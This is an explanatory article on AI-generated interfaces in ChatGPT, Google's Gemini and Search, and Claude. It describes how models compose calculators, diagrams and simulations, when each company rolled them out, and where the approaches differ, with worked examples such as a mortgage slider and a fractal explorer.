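# ChatGPT's Intelligent UI and rival generated interfaces from Google, Anthropic and others

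## What a generated interface is

A generated interface is a screen element or page that an AI model makes or assembles for one request, rather than one that people designed and built in advance. It may be a chart, a form, a calculator, or a whole web page with its own buttons. The industry mostly calls it generative UI (user interface). During 2025 and 2026, OpenAI added some version of it to ChatGPT, Google to its Gemini app and search engine, and Anthropic to Claude.

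Definitions of a generated interface differ in how much of it the model must create. *Generative UI* (Leviathan, Valevski and colleagues, 2025), Google's announcement of its own research system, describes a model that produces "not only content but an entire user experience". *Generative Interfaces for Language Models* (Chen, Zhang and colleagues, 2025), from Stanford, also describes entirely new interface structures. Google Cloud's *What is Generative UI?* uses a broader definition, which includes systems that only pick from a fixed set of hand-built parts. The broader definition works better for comparing products, because one of the main differences between them is how much the model may invent.

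### One loan, in paragraphs and with a slider

Suppose someone who wants to borrow $300,000 for a house at 6% a year asks an assistant whether to repay over 15 years or 30. The assistant can answer this well in text, without a slider. The 30-year loan costs about $1,799 a month and $347,500 in total interest, while the 15-year loan costs about $2,532 a month and $155,700 in total interest. The borrower would save roughly $192,000 with the 15-year loan by paying $733 more each month.

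Text becomes awkward when the borrower wants to compare options. If $2,532 a month is too much, they may ask about a 20-year term (about $2,149 a month, and $215,800 in interest), then about a 6.5% rate. Each variation requires another message, another wait and another paragraph, and by the fourth the borrower is scrolling back up to find the earlier figures. The model could print a table of every term and rate, but twenty terms by ten rates makes 200 cells, of which the borrower wants three or four. Chen and colleagues say text is weak for exploratory tasks and for dense information spread over many turns. Google Cloud calls this the "wall of text problem".

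All of those monthly payments come from one formula:

M = P × r / (1 − (1 + r)^−n)

P is the amount borrowed, r the monthly interest rate, n the number of months and M the monthly payment. A calculator with a slider stores this formula and recalculates the result whenever the borrower moves the slider. PPC Land, a marketing news site, describes such a tool in Google Search, which has sliders for the amount, rate and term and shows the monthly payment and total interest. In *Google Search with Gemini 3*, Google's head of search, Reid (2025), introduced the feature with nearly the same example, a loan calculator built into the answer for comparing two mortgages.

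The model's work ends when it finishes the calculator, so it does no arithmetic while the slider moves. This makes the tool fast, but it also means one mistake can affect more figures. An error in a text answer may affect only one figure, whereas an error in the formula, such as using a yearly rate instead of a monthly one, makes every figure the tool shows wrong, and they all look equally tidy. The slider also gives no advice. Whether someone with an unsteady income should commit to $2,532 a month needs a written explanation, so a useful answer to the loan question probably includes both text and a calculator.

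### How a model that writes text makes a button

A language model outputs only tokens, the short pieces of text that make up its replies. A program on the user's device, either a web browser or the assistant's own app, reads this text and displays what it specifies. Chat apps have long used this method for formatting. For example, when the model writes a word between asterisks, the app shows the word in bold. In a generated interface, the model's text specifies working controls, which the model can either describe or write as code.

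A description relies on components. A component is a ready-made interface part, such as a button, chart, tab or form field, and a component library is the fixed set of components from which a model may compose an answer. The model names the part it wants and fills in the settings, usually in JSON, a plain-text format for labelled values. For the length of the loan it might write:

```
{"component": "slider", "label": "Years", "min": 10, "max": 30, "value": 30}
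```

The app then draws its own slider, which programmers wrote and tested beforehand, with the ends set at 10 and 30. The same line can produce different sliders in a browser and on a phone, each in the style of its device. Google Cloud counts this among the advantages of A2UI, Google's open format for such descriptions. The line does not contain the loan formula, so moving the slider does nothing unless the library already includes a loan calculator or the format can express simple calculations.

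Free code is web code that the model writes from scratch for a request. It comes in three languages: HTML for what is on the page, CSS for how it looks, and JavaScript for what it does. The same slider in HTML is:

```
<input type="range" min="10" max="30" value="30">
```

A few lines of JavaScript after it would hold the formula and update the figures with each movement. The browser runs all this like any other web page. The research system that Leviathan and colleagues built at Google works this way. The model isn't limited to a library of components, so it can make things that few libraries would include, such as Reid's example of a simulation of three bodies pulling on one another by gravity, with variables the user can change.

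The drawback is that the user's device runs a program that no person has read. Google Cloud warns in particular of cross-site scripting, in which malicious code runs inside a page that the user trusts. A product can limit the danger with a sandbox, where code runs without access to the rest of the page or to the user's account.

Real systems mix descriptions and free code. Google Cloud distinguishes between a model selecting a finished, hand-built part and a model laying out cards and lists through a description, though both use ready-made components. Chen and colleagues come closer to a blend by giving the model a stock of reusable clocks, maps, calculators and charts that it can use when writing the web code for the whole page.

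An interface on the screen has to remember things such as ticked boxes and entered numbers, which make up its state. Chen and colleagues treat each component as a finite state machine and write each machine as M = (S, E, δ, s₀). S is the set of states the component can be in, and E is the set of events it can receive, such as a click. The rule δ gives the next state for each combination of state and event, and s₀ is the starting state. For the loan slider, S is the whole numbers of years from 10 to 30, and s₀ is 30. If the user drags the slider from 30 to 20, δ gives 20 as the next state. A second layer represents the whole interface as a graph, in which the points are views and the arrows are the moves a user can make between them. In their example, a request to understand quantum physics leads from a home view to tutorials, then to a simulation and a glossary.

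Keeping track of the interface's state is a practical problem that text answers never had. The slider's position is stored on the user's device, and the model doesn't receive it unless the product sends it back. If the borrower has settled on 20 years and asks "can I afford this one?", the reply may be about the wrong loan.

Speed is harder too. Chat products hide the slowness of their models by streaming, which means showing an answer piece by piece as the model writes it. This works for text because people can start reading an unfinished paragraph, but an unfinished calculator is mostly unusable even if it appears on screen. When Google announced its research system in November 2025, Leviathan and colleagues acknowledged that it sometimes took a minute or more to produce a result. Descriptions suit streaming better because the model can send them as separate, self-contained lines, so the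 app can draw the first card while the model is still writing the third.

The last basic term is surface, the place in a product where an answer appears, such as a chat thread or a search results page. Google has several, including AI Overviews, the AI-written answers on its ordinary results page, and AI Mode, Search's separate conversational mode. In an example from *5 new ways to level up your learning with Search* (Verma, 2026), a search for "ph scale" brings up an interactive visual in an AI Overview. A follow-up request to plot citrus fruits on the scale goes to AI Mode, which builds a new version of the visual for that question.

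### Generated interfaces, fixed widgets and outside apps

Not every interactive card in an AI's reply is a generated interface. Anthropic's *Claude now creates interactive charts, diagrams and visualizations* (2026) describes three kinds of interface in Claude. When a user asks how compound interest works, Claude generates an interactive curve for that conversation, which changes or disappears as the conversation moves on. When a user asks about the weather, Claude shows a visual that Anthropic designed for weather questions in general. Recipes also have a set format, with ingredients and steps. Users can also work in Figma, Canva or Slack within the conversation, through interfaces supplied by the companies that run those services. Claude is then only the host, the application that displays another company's interface.

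ChatGPT gained one of each in fifteen days, according to OpenAI's *ChatGPT release notes* (2026). On September 22 it got flashcards, which users tap to flip and then mark as known or not. The model writes the text, but the flipping and marking work the same way for everybody, so this is a fixed widget with generated contents. On September 29 plugins, which connect ChatGPT to outside services, gained their own interactive panels and forms. Intelligent UI followed on October 7, letting ChatGPT put together a comparison, a diagram or a bill splitter to fit the question.

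Appearance does not always show which kind of interface a user is looking at. OpenAI offers outside developers a library of ready-made buttons, cards and input controls that match ChatGPT's style, so another company's panel can pass for ChatGPT's work. It is more useful to ask who fixed the layout and when. Anthropic's designers settled the weather visual before any user asked for it, so they had the chance to test it. Figma is responsible for its own panel. A model generated the compound-interest curve seconds before the user saw it, and that user may be the first to try it. Developers ordinarily test an interface by comparing screenshots with an approved version, but this does not work when the layout is never the same twice. Google Cloud therefore advises them to check that the necessary button is present and works, wherever the model put it.

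Some cases are hard to classify. Google Search now makes practice quizzes on request, with new questions and explanations, but a user can't easily tell whether the interface around them is also newly generated. Claude can make artifacts, which are documents, pages or tools kept separate from the text of its reply. An interactive artifact is a generated interface by any reasonable definition, but it lasts beyond the question that prompted it, and users can share or download it.

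### From a side window to the ordinary answer

The main dates are these:

- **June 20, 2024:** Anthropic launched Artifacts, which, as Fortune (2024) reported that day, put the code, text or designs that a user requested into a window beside the conversation.
- **November 18, 2025:** Google introduced generative UI in the Gemini app and in AI Mode.
- **March 12, 2026:** Anthropic began a beta of temporary charts and diagrams inside Claude's replies.
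- **August 19, 2026:** Google announced that generative UI had started to reach AI Overviews.
- **October 7, 2026:** OpenAI released Intelligent UI in ChatGPT together with its GPT-6 model, for paying users first and for free users from the next day.

Models could already write a working web page in 2024 and have become much better at it since. Leviathan and colleagues found that the quality of generated interfaces depends strongly on the underlying model. The products' defaults have also changed. When Artifacts first launched, users had to ask for a document or a website design to get one. Claude's newer visuals are on by default, and Claude chooses when to draw one. ChatGPT also chooses the format, which may still be plain text, and Google's model adds a tool when it determines that one would help.

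The audience has also widened. In November 2025, Google limited generative UI in AI Mode to paying subscribers in the United States. By August 2026, it was available in AI Mode to English-language users worldwide and was being added to the ordinary results page, the larger of the two surfaces according to Search Engine Journal's *Google Expands Generative UI Beyond AI Mode Into AI Overviews* (2026). People who have never opened an AI assistant can now encounter a generated interface through an ordinary search.

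### Where the approaches part

The companies agree that people can use an answer as well as read it, but they differ on how much of the interface the model may invent and how long the result should last. A fixed component library keeps answers consistent and safe, but it can show only what its designers anticipated. If the model writes code freely, it can show almost anything, though the result may be broken or unsafe. A budget chart that disappears with the conversation is little use to someone who wants to reopen it next month.

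In Google's own study, raters strongly preferred generated pages to plain text answers, but Leviathan and colleagues left waiting time out of the comparison. Waiting is a large part of the burden on users, so the study doesn't settle whether they are better off with generated pages. If users still prefer these pages after waiting for them, the pages may compete with other people's products. Leviathan and colleagues look forward to users no longer having to choose from a catalogue of existing applications, and Search Engine Journal points out that websites built around calculators and converters now overlap with what Google generates on demand.

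The future role of chat is also unclear. The borrower with the slider typed only one question. If many answers work like that, people might use chat mainly to call up tools, or they might still use it to say what they want and ask what the numbers mean.

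## OpenAI's approach: answers composed inside the chat

OpenAI put its generated interfaces into the ordinary ChatGPT reply. A diagram or a calculator appears with the text, so the user doesn't have to open another window or know that the feature exists. In a help article quoted in Digital Matters' *GPT-6 and Intelligent UI in ChatGPT* (2026), OpenAI promises to give each answer "the right layout, visuals, and interactivity". A comparison of two phones might appear in side-by-side columns, but a question about the capital of Peru should still get a short text answer.

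Wheatley (2026) covered OpenAI's October 7 press briefing in *With GPT-6, ChatGPT's responses are much more visually appealing and interactive*. At the briefing, Aarush Selvan, an OpenAI product manager, said that ChatGPT had "predominantly been a text-based interface". Selvan argued that "the most helpful answers aren't just text" when someone is planning a meal or a trip, or learning something.

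The model picks the format, which is the more distinctive part of the case. People rarely know which format would help them before they have seen the answer, and few would think to ask for a slider. The model is already working out the content, so it is reasonably well placed to choose a suitable layout. Users who get plain text can still ask for something more interactive, and ChatGPT will rework the answer.

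This approach depends on the model correctly identifying when interaction is worth the space. A user who gets text when a diagram would have been better can ask again, but someone who wanted one sentence and got a diagram with five tabs has to search the tabs for it.

OpenAI built up to Intelligent UI gradually. It merged ChatGPT's voice and text modes into a single view, where maps and other visuals could appear during a spoken conversation (Digital Watch, *New ChatGPT layout blends audio, text and maps in one view*). When the company later gave image-making its own area in the app, Simo, one of its executives, explained in *The shift from text to more dynamic AI experiences* that the chat interface wasn't designed for that kind of work. Visual answers followed in February 2026 and flashcards in September. Each addition handled one kind of content or task, whereas Intelligent UI is meant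 to work for any question.

### What OpenAI demonstrated

In the main demonstration, according to Wheatley, the user asked how to piece together a seven-speed bicycle. ChatGPT drew the bicycle from the side, with tabs for the frame, wheels, drivetrain, brakes and cockpit (the handlebars and the parts around them). Tapping a part brings up an explanation of what it does. This is a good way to learn the names and functions of the parts. It is less obviously a good answer to the question, because someone assembling a bicycle needs to know the order of the steps, which a labelled diagram doesn't show.

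For a Sunday roast, ChatGPT produced a lamb recipe with pictures of the dishes, cooking times, a timed checklist and a control for the number of guests, which recalculates the shopping list. Most ingredients scale in proportion to the number of guests, so if 2 kg of lamb feeds six, nine need 3 kg. Cooking time follows a different rule, commonly 20 minutes per 500 grams plus another 20 for roast lamb, so the 2 kg joint takes 100 minutes and the 3 kg joint takes 140. If a tool updated the shopping list but not the checklist, the cook would take the larger joint out 40 minutes early. Digital Matters mentions only the shopping list as changing with the guest count, so it's unclear whether the timings change too.

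ChatGPT showed the road trip as stops on a map, with notes on which detours were worth taking. OpenAI also showed a bill splitter, a retirement savings calculator and a retro game that users can play in the chat.

The Monty Hall problem is probably the best example for Selvan's claim that the feature makes complex topics easier to learn. A contestant picks one of three doors, one of which hides a prize. The host, who knows where the prize is, opens a different door with nothing behind it and offers a swap. Swapping wins two times in three, which many people refuse to believe when they read it. OpenAI's version lets the reader change an input and see the result. If the input is the number of doors, n, and the host opens every losing door but one, swapping wins with probability (n − 1)/n, which is 67% for three doors, 90% for ten and 99% for a hundred. Readers can then keep adding doors until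 the result convinces them, which they can't do with a written explanation.

OpenAI chose these examples, so they show what the system can make when it works well, but not how often everyday questions get answers this polished.

### A component library and a compiler

OpenAI has only outlined how Intelligent UI works. The company says in its launch announcement, quoted by Digital Matters, that it built "a library of native, streamable components" and a compiler that draws the interface while the model is still writing. Intelligent UI therefore belongs mainly with systems in which a model describes an interface and the app builds it from ready-made parts.

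"Native" normally means the ChatGPT app draws the component with its own buttons and fonts, instead of loading a small web page inside the chat. "Streamable" means a component can appear before its description is complete. A compiler translates instructions from one form into another, and this one turns the model's output into what appears on the screen.

Drawing half a description is harder than it sounds. A line of JSON like the one for the loan slider is invalid until its closing bracket arrives, and an ordinary program would reject it as broken. A streaming compiler has to do something sensible with the fragment. OpenAI hasn't published its format, but for the road trip the process would go roughly like this:

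1. The model writes that the answer needs a map, and the app draws an empty one.
2. The model writes the name and position of the first stop, and a pin appears.
3. Each further stop adds a pin, and the app zooms out to fit them all.
4. The model marks the end of the map and goes back to writing prose.

This works because the app already has a definition of a map that includes stops, so it can show three stops before the fourth arrives. It has no such definition for free-form code, and an unfinished JavaScript function can't run.

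The model also has to learn to use the library. OpenAI says that it trained GPT-6 on what an answer should contain, how to lay it out and when to make it interactive. Wheatley writes that the models were "pretrained on" the components. Pretraining usually means the first stage of training, on huge amounts of general text, and a product's component library seems more likely to come in later. Either way, a model that has learned the library in training doesn't need to be given instructions for every component with each question. However, it may need more training before it can use a new component well.

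OpenAI evaluated the results for clarity, usefulness and completeness. These goals can conflict. Each tab in the bicycle diagram makes it more complete but somewhat less clear for someone with one question about brakes. OpenAI hasn't said how the answers scored, so outsiders can't tell how often an interactive answer beat a plain one in its tests, or how often the model chose the wrong format. Google did publish its raters' preferences for its research system.

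OpenAI also hasn't explained how it renders the games. A retro game has to redraw moving objects many times a second and detect when they collide, which charts, tabs and form fields can't do. The component library may include a game component that takes the rules as settings, in which case ChatGPT can offer only variations on games that OpenAI planned for. Or the model may write code for the game, which the app runs in a sandbox. In that case, the component library doesn't really limit what ChatGPT can show.

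Calculators raise a milder version of the same question, since either the component or the model has to supply the formula. Digital Matters advises organisations to verify a tool's figures before using them in budgets or board papers, because its polished look can make it seem more authoritative than it is. Leaving out a relevant figure may be a bigger problem than wrong arithmetic. If someone saves $500 a month for 30 years at 6% a year, compounded monthly, a correct calculator shows about $502,000. If prices rise by 2% a year, that sum will buy what about $277,000 buys today. Both figures are right, but a person planning for retirement needs the second one, and checking the calculator's arithmetic won't reveal that it's missing.

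### Answering while still thinking

GPT-6 also changed the timing of answers in the Chat tab. Reasoning models ordinarily finish their reasoning, which the user mostly doesn't see, and any web searches before the first word of the answer appears. OpenAI wrote in its announcement that GPT-6 "can interleave thinking with answering". It can start its reply, go back to reasoning or searching, and then add what it finds without another prompt from the user.

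In the road trip example, the model could start with the obvious route, look up road closures while the user reads about the first stop, and add a warning further down.

OpenAI says answers that need a web search start 44% sooner with Instant, the fastest setting. For example, an answer that used to begin after nine seconds would now begin after about five. OpenAI measured this itself, and the figure covers only when an answer starts, so the full answer may not finish any sooner.

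When the model starts answering early, it writes the opening before the search is finished, and the user may already be acting on that text. If the search then contradicts the opening, the model has to correct it further down, and some readers will have stopped by then. Starting early is still likely to be worth it for most everyday questions, where the opening is seldom wrong.

The two changes work well together because the user can read a few sentences of text while waiting for a calculator to be ready. Components may also be easier than prose to update with late findings. If a search turns up a fourth phone worth comparing, the app can add a column, whereas a paragraph that began "there are three good options" would have to be corrected.

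### Who has it

OpenAI released Intelligent UI worldwide, but only in the Chat tab, where people hold ordinary conversations. It isn't available in ChatGPT Work, which makes documents and carries out longer tasks, or in Codex, which is for programming. The table combines the launch terms with the thinking levels from OpenAI's guide to its models, *GPT-6 and other models in ChatGPT*. At higher levels, the model reasons for longer.

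| Plan | Model in Chat at launch | Start | Levels below Pro |
|---|---|---|---|
| Free, Go | GPT-6 Luna | October 8 | Instant, plus a "Think" button |
| Plus | GPT-6 Sol | October 7 | Instant to High |
| Pro, Business, Enterprise | GPT-6 Sol | October 7 | Instant to Extra High |

OpenAI calls its fastest and cheapest models Luna. Intelligent UI works from Instant through Extra High, and an answer with a calculator counts against the same usage allowances as any other. Digital Matters found no mention of Edu, the plan for universities, in the October notes.

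The exception is the Pro level, which runs on a different model, GPT-6 Astra, and doesn't support Intelligent UI. People who pay for the most thorough reasoning therefore lose interactive answers whenever they use it, even though a chart might help most in a long, difficult analysis. Access to GPT-6 Sol doesn't guarantee Intelligent UI either. The model had been available in Work and Codex since September 22, and the October release changed nothing there.

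Intelligent UI runs on the web and in up-to-date mobile apps, but not in the older ChatGPT desktop apps for macOS and Windows. OpenAI tells people who still use those apps to go to the website.

Sources disagree on which model free users have now. OpenAI's launch notes put the Free and Go plans on GPT-6 Luna, as does a plan table in AI Toolbox's *ChatGPT Models Explained*, which the vendor checked on October 28. But OpenAI's guide, as it stood on December 5, puts both plans on the older GPT-5.6 Luna. The guide probably contains old text, since it still describes GPT-5.6 Luna as "becoming the default model" for those plans. It also ties Intelligent UI to GPT-6, so if its plan information were current, free users would have lost the feature.

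After the launch, OpenAI introduced a newer model for paying users, GPT-6.2, on November 17. The guide now lists it for Instant and the thinking levels in Chat, with access arriving as the rollout reaches each account. Pro stays on GPT-6 Astra, so the gap there remains. The guide still describes Intelligent UI as a feature of "GPT-6" and has no separate terms for 6.2.

On December 2 OpenAI also announced a redesigned mobile app for Plus, Pro and Business subscribers. KBY Technologies' *ChatGPT's Redesigned Mobile App Reaches Plus Users* describes only navigation changes. Users can pin favourite features to the tab bar, and there is a new More tab. These changes affect where people find ChatGPT's tools, not how it composes answers.

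### Turning it down, and what a chat keeps

Users who find the new answers too busy can reduce the visual elements by setting "Visual answers" to "Simple" under Personalization, though OpenAI gives instructions only for the web version. OpenAI warns that some visual elements may still appear and that the setting doesn't bring back a text-only mode. Paying users can also pick GPT-5.6 Sol from the model menu, which keeps the conversation on that model. This should avoid Intelligent UI, which comes with GPT-6, but it means using an older model.

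Companies have even less choice. Enterprise administrators can switch off access to GPT-6 Sol. OpenAI's *ChatGPT Enterprise and Edu models and limits* says that the levels a person sees in Chat depend on the workspace's settings and that person's role, so an administrator could withhold the model from only some staff. Digital Matters looked for a separate switch for Intelligent UI and found none. A finance department that wanted the better model but didn't want its staff relying on unchecked calculators would need a written policy.

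According to the help article, as Digital Matters reports it, checklists can survive a refresh of the chat, but an interface's state doesn't carry over from one chat to another. The cook who has ticked off the potatoes and then reloads the page should find them still ticked. If the cook asks for the roast again in a new chat the following Sunday, the checklist starts empty, and any corrections to the guest count or the timings stay in the old conversation. Checklists are the only example Digital Matters gives of a component that keeps its state, so a user who has typed twenty figures into a retirement calculator would be wise to write down the result.

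This suits an answer made for one question, and it avoids some confusion because last month's budget can't carry over into this month's. It also makes Intelligent UI a poor fit for anything a person wants to use repeatedly, but OpenAI has other features for that. ChatGPT automatically saves flashcard decks to the user's library, so a student can return to them weeks later. Since September 29, eligible Pro, Business and Enterprise users have also been able to turn a conversation into a Page, a shared document that colleagues can edit and comment on. ChatGPT can add charts and interactive content to it.

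## Google's approach: pages written for the question, in Gemini and Search

Google's researchers have their model write a complete web page for each question, whereas OpenAI gave GPT-6 a library of components. The model writes the layout, the controls and the requests for pictures in free-form code. Leviathan and colleagues call the result an entire user experience. In one of their examples, a page about the microbiome for a five-year-old needs different features, as well as different wording, from one for an adult.

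The main argument for generating pages this way is that it can serve questions nobody designs for. Product managers, designers and engineers take a long time to build a good interface, so companies build them for broad, common requests, such as weather forecasts. Leviathan and colleagues' test prompts included planning stargazing parties from Chicago and playing billiards with the planets, and no company would assign a team to either. Even a cheap human-made page costs too much for one person's question. The researchers hired freelance developers to make pages for comparison, and each page cost $100 to $130 and took about three to five hours, while the model takes a minute or two.

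They hope interfaces will change the way text has. People once had to choose among existing texts, but a language model can now write one for their immediate need.

They also concede that the model is less competent than human experts. This hardly matters for the stargazing party, because no expert would have built that page and the realistic alternative is a text answer. It matters more for common questions, where a company could afford to build one good page by hand and show it to everyone.

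### From the question to the page

The system announced in November 2025 uses Gemini 3 Pro, then Google's newest model. Google added a long set of standing instructions, a server that gives the model access to tools, and small programs that repair the page before the user sees it.

Leviathan and colleagues published an early version of the instructions, about 3,000 words long. Under these instructions, the model should build an interactive application even when a sentence would do. If someone asks the time, it should write a clock that keeps running. If someone types "ant colony", it should write a simulation with sliders for the number of ants and the sources of food. The model must not make up data or include buttons that do nothing, and it must search the web for any facts about particular people, places or organisations.

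One of the examples in the instructions is a visitor to Singapore who wants a sightseeing jog of up to 10 km from a hotel. The system would handle the request roughly like this:

1. The model decides what kind of application fits, in this case a map with routes.
2. It lists the facts and pictures it needs, such as the position of the hotel and the sights nearby.
3. It searches the web for the facts, and searches again if the first results raise new questions.
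4. It thinks of about a dozen features, drops those that are weak or that it can't verify, and keeps the rest.
5. It writes the whole page, with one to three routes drawn on the map and buttons to highlight each.
6. The repair programs correct the code, and the user's browser displays the page.

Search results go back to the model, which has to read them before it can write. Pictures can take a shorter route. The model writes an ordinary image tag with a description of the picture inside the address, for example:

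```
<img src="/gen?prompt=runner+beside+a+river+at+dawn" alt="A runner by a river">
```

When the browser loads the page, it requests this address, and Google's server generates the picture and sends it straight to the browser. The model doesn't have to wait for the picture, but it also can't check it for mistakes. A second kind of address fetches an existing picture from the web. The instructions limit generated pictures to generic scenes and world-famous landmarks, and require the model to search for pictures of named people and lesser-known places. This is sensible, since a generated picture of the visitor's hotel wouldn't show the real building.

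The image generator has no access to the rest of the page. In a picture story about a friendly alien, the model must therefore repeat the alien's full description, including the number of eyes, in every image request, or the alien may change from one picture to the next.

The instructions also forbid the page's code from accessing the product that displays it or using the browser's storage. Without storage, anything the user types into the page is likely to be lost when they close it. If the user asks for a change, the model edits its earlier code but has to write out the full page again, so adding one more sight to the jogging map takes about as much writing as making the map did.

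The repair programs deal with the model's common mistakes. Leviathan and colleagues list nine from an early prototype. One replaces a placeholder with the real access key that Google Maps requires. Another adds code that reports errors from the user's browser. Others replace icons that the model invented, or remove source citations that it put in the middle of its JavaScript, where they could stop the program from running.

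All nine concern whether the page works, and none checks facts or formulas, so a map with an 11 km route would go through unchanged. Accuracy depends on the model following its instructions to search and verify. The researchers acknowledged occasional inaccuracies when they announced the system.

The strength of the model seems to matter more than the system around it. On everyday prompts sampled from LMArena, a public site for comparing chatbots, Gemini 2.0 Flash-Lite made errors in 60% of its outputs and Gemini 2.0 Flash in 29%. The researchers found no errors with Gemini 2.5 or Gemini 3. But the sample had only 92 prompts, so a fault that affects one page in a hundred would have had about a 40% chance of not appearing, and the researchers warn that coding errors still occur occasionally. The long instructions made a smaller difference. Raters preferred pages made with them to pages made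 from a minimal prompt in about 58% of comparisons, the equivalent of a 57-point lead on the Elo scale used in chess.

### A page about fractals

In one of Google's published examples, a user asked for an explanation of fractals in as much depth as possible. Fractals are shapes with detail at every scale, and in many of them each part resembles the whole. The system produced a page called "Fractal Explorer", with several interactive tools, a section on practical uses, and a history from the nineteenth-century mathematician Karl Weierstrass to Benoit Mandelbrot.

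One tool is a calculator for a fractal's dimension. If a shape consists of N copies of itself, each smaller by a factor of s, its dimension is:

D = log N / log s

Cutting a square into 9 smaller squares, each a third as wide, gives log 9 / log 3 = 2, the expected dimension of a square. To draw the edge of the Koch snowflake, one repeatedly replaces the middle third of every line with two sides of a small triangle, so each line becomes four lines a third as long. The formula gives a dimension of log 4 / log 3, or about 1.26, which is between the dimensions of a line and a surface.

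A slider on the page builds the snowflake one step at a time. Each step makes the outline a third longer, so after ten steps it is nearly 18 times its original length, yet it still fits in the same space on the screen. Moving the slider makes this easier to believe than a written explanation does.

The most ambitious tool links two drawings, the Mandelbrot set and a Julia set. Both come from repeating the rule z → z² + c, where z and c are complex numbers, which can be pictured as points on a plane. The Mandelbrot set contains every c for which z stays within bounds when it starts at zero. A Julia set keeps c fixed and shows how the result depends on the starting value of z. On Google's page, moving the mouse over the Mandelbrot set changes c and redraws the matching Julia set. If the drawing is 400 by 400 points and the page repeats the rule up to 100 times per point, each redraw takes up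 to 16 million steps. The user's browser does this work without using the model again.

This prompt suits the system unusually well because the user wanted depth and the subject is visual. The researchers' test prompts also include "is 897 prime?" A good answer is "No, 897 = 3 × 13 × 23", and taking a minute to build a page would only delay it. Google's products therefore need to let either the user or the model decide when a page is worth making.

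### The Gemini app: from a menu to the ordinary reply

Google first left the choice to the user. On November 18, 2025, it added two experiments to the Gemini app, dynamic view and visual layout. Google said people might at first see only one of them, so that it could compare the two.

Dynamic view is the product version of the research system. Google's *Gemini 3 brings upgraded smarts and new capabilities to the Gemini app* demonstrates it with a Van Gogh gallery in which the user can tap each painting to learn what was happening in the artist's life. Visual layout looks more like a magazine article, with photos and interactive modules. If the user requests a three-day trip to Rome, it produces an illustrated itinerary that they can adjust through the modules.

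Google built visual layout with Flutter, its toolkit for making apps. A related kit lets outside developers generate interfaces from their own catalogue of ready-made parts. Visual layout probably works similarly, which would make it closer to OpenAI's Intelligent UI than to dynamic view, even though both Google features appeared in the same menu.

To use either feature, a person opens the Gemini website on a computer, clicks "Tools", selects the feature and types a prompt, according to Google's *Use visual layout or dynamic view in Gemini Apps*. As of April 2026, dynamic view didn't work in the mobile app. Dynamic view can generate new pictures, which count towards the user's daily image generation limit, whereas visual layout uses existing photos from approved websites, which don't count.

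Requiring people to select a tool from a menu spares them pages they don't want, but people who never open the menu never get a generated page.

On April 9, 2026, Google added interactive simulations to Gemini conversations. They were available worldwide, but not yet to school accounts or accounts for Workspace, Google's office software. Users no longer needed the Tools menu, but they still had to select the Pro model and ask for a simulation in their prompt. Google's *The Gemini app can now generate interactive simulations and models* (2026) suggests starting the prompt with "show me" or "help me visualize".

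In Google's example, the user changes the moon's initial speed and the strength of gravity to see which combinations produce a stable orbit. The speed for a circular orbit is:

v = √(GM/r)

G is the gravitational constant, M the mass of the Earth and r the distance between the two bodies. For the real moon, v is about 1.02 km a second. At √2 times that speed, about 1.44 km a second, the moon would escape. Users can test the simulation against these figures. If the moon stays in orbit at 1.6 km a second with realistic settings, something in the code is wrong. But most people who ask for the simulation won't know the figures.

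Google redesigned the Gemini app in May. Gemini now puts the most important information at the top in bold, and 9to5Google (2026) reported that replies would include timelines, narrated videos and interactive visualizations "when relevant". With this change, users began to receive interactive answers without asking for them. In *Google expands Gemini's interactive models to even more users*, McNeal (2026) reported that Workspace customers who met a minimum age got the April simulations in August.

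### AI Mode: the user picks a model, and the model picks the format

Generated interfaces reached AI Mode on the same day as the Gemini app, but the choices were split differently between the user and the system. 9to5Google reported that subscribers to Google's AI Pro and Ultra plans in the United States had to select "Thinking" from a menu, where the label also included "generative layouts". The system then determined for each question whether to build a tool. In Google's demonstration, the user asked how RNA polymerase, the enzyme that copies DNA into RNA, works. The prompt also asked about the stages of the process and how it differs between bacteria and more complex cells, but didn't mention a diagram or a simulation.

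There is some confusion about who could use the feature at first. Search Engine Journal later wrote that Google had tied the Gemini 3 Pro model to a subscription, without saying that generated interfaces needed one too. But Leviathan and colleagues explicitly listed generated interfaces in AI Mode as available to Pro and Ultra subscribers in the United States.

At its I/O conference in May 2026, Google promised to bring the feature to everyone in Search that summer, free of charge. AI Mode had more than a billion monthly users by then, according to Google's *A new era for AI Search*. Google also described the technology differently, saying Search would use Gemini 3.5 Flash, a faster kind of model than Gemini 3 Pro, and Antigravity, its system for letting AI agents write software. Search would design layouts by "assembling components" such as tables, graphs and simulations.

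That sounds less like writing each page from scratch. A table is easy to prepare in advance, but a simulation of how somebody's watch works, another of Google's examples, presumably isn't. Search most likely combines ready-made parts with code that the model writes when no part fits. If so, the research paper only partly describes what Search does now. Google also announced trackers and dashboards that users could return to, available first to American subscribers.

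Interactive visuals in AI Mode were still limited to subscribers on June 9, according to *AI Mode in Google Search will soon let everyone build interactive diagrams* (McNeal, 2026). By then, Google was promoting them with a visual about soccer formations, in which the user moves things around to see how each formation works. Google opened the feature to everyone using AI Mode in English on August 19.

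People can also ask AI Mode for an interface directly. Verma advises those with a very specific question to go straight to AI Mode and describe the tool or visual they need. For example, a teacher could ask for a pH scale that shows only citrus fruits.

### AI Overviews: an interface that nobody requested

In AI Overviews, Verma's pH visual can appear above the links after an ordinary search, without the user choosing a model or describing a tool. The rollout began on August 19, 2026, and Google expected to complete it within weeks. According to Search Engine Journal, the result is usually a custom visual layout and only sometimes includes an interactive tool. Google hadn't said which searches would bring up a generated interface.

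The argument about questions that nobody designs for is weaker here, because students everywhere search for the pH scale and Google could have asked a designer and a chemistry teacher to build one excellent version. Verma doesn't say whether Google generates a new visual for each search or stores one and reuses it. Storing it would be quicker and would let people check it first, but then it would hardly differ from a fixed widget.

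The follow-up about citrus fruits is a better use of the technology, because few people ask for it and the answer benefits from being visual. It also shows what can go wrong. Each step on the pH scale is a factor of ten, so if lemon juice has a pH of 2 and orange juice a pH of 4, the lemon juice has 100 times the concentration of hydrogen ions. On an evenly spaced scale, the two fruits are only two marks apart. A teacher building the visual would probably add a note about this, but a generated version might not include one.

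### Models and languages in late 2026

Google Search moved to a new default model, Gemini 4 Hydrogen, on November 12, 2026. *Google Search gets a major upgrade with Gemini 4 Hydrogen* (Stein, 2026) announced the change for users worldwide and promised more visual answers. These include comparison tables and interactive tools that fit the question, according to *Google brings Gemini 4 Hydrogen to Search with smarter answers* (Sood, 2026). The default model now generates interfaces for free, whereas a year earlier American users had to pay for a plan and select a particular model to get one in Search.

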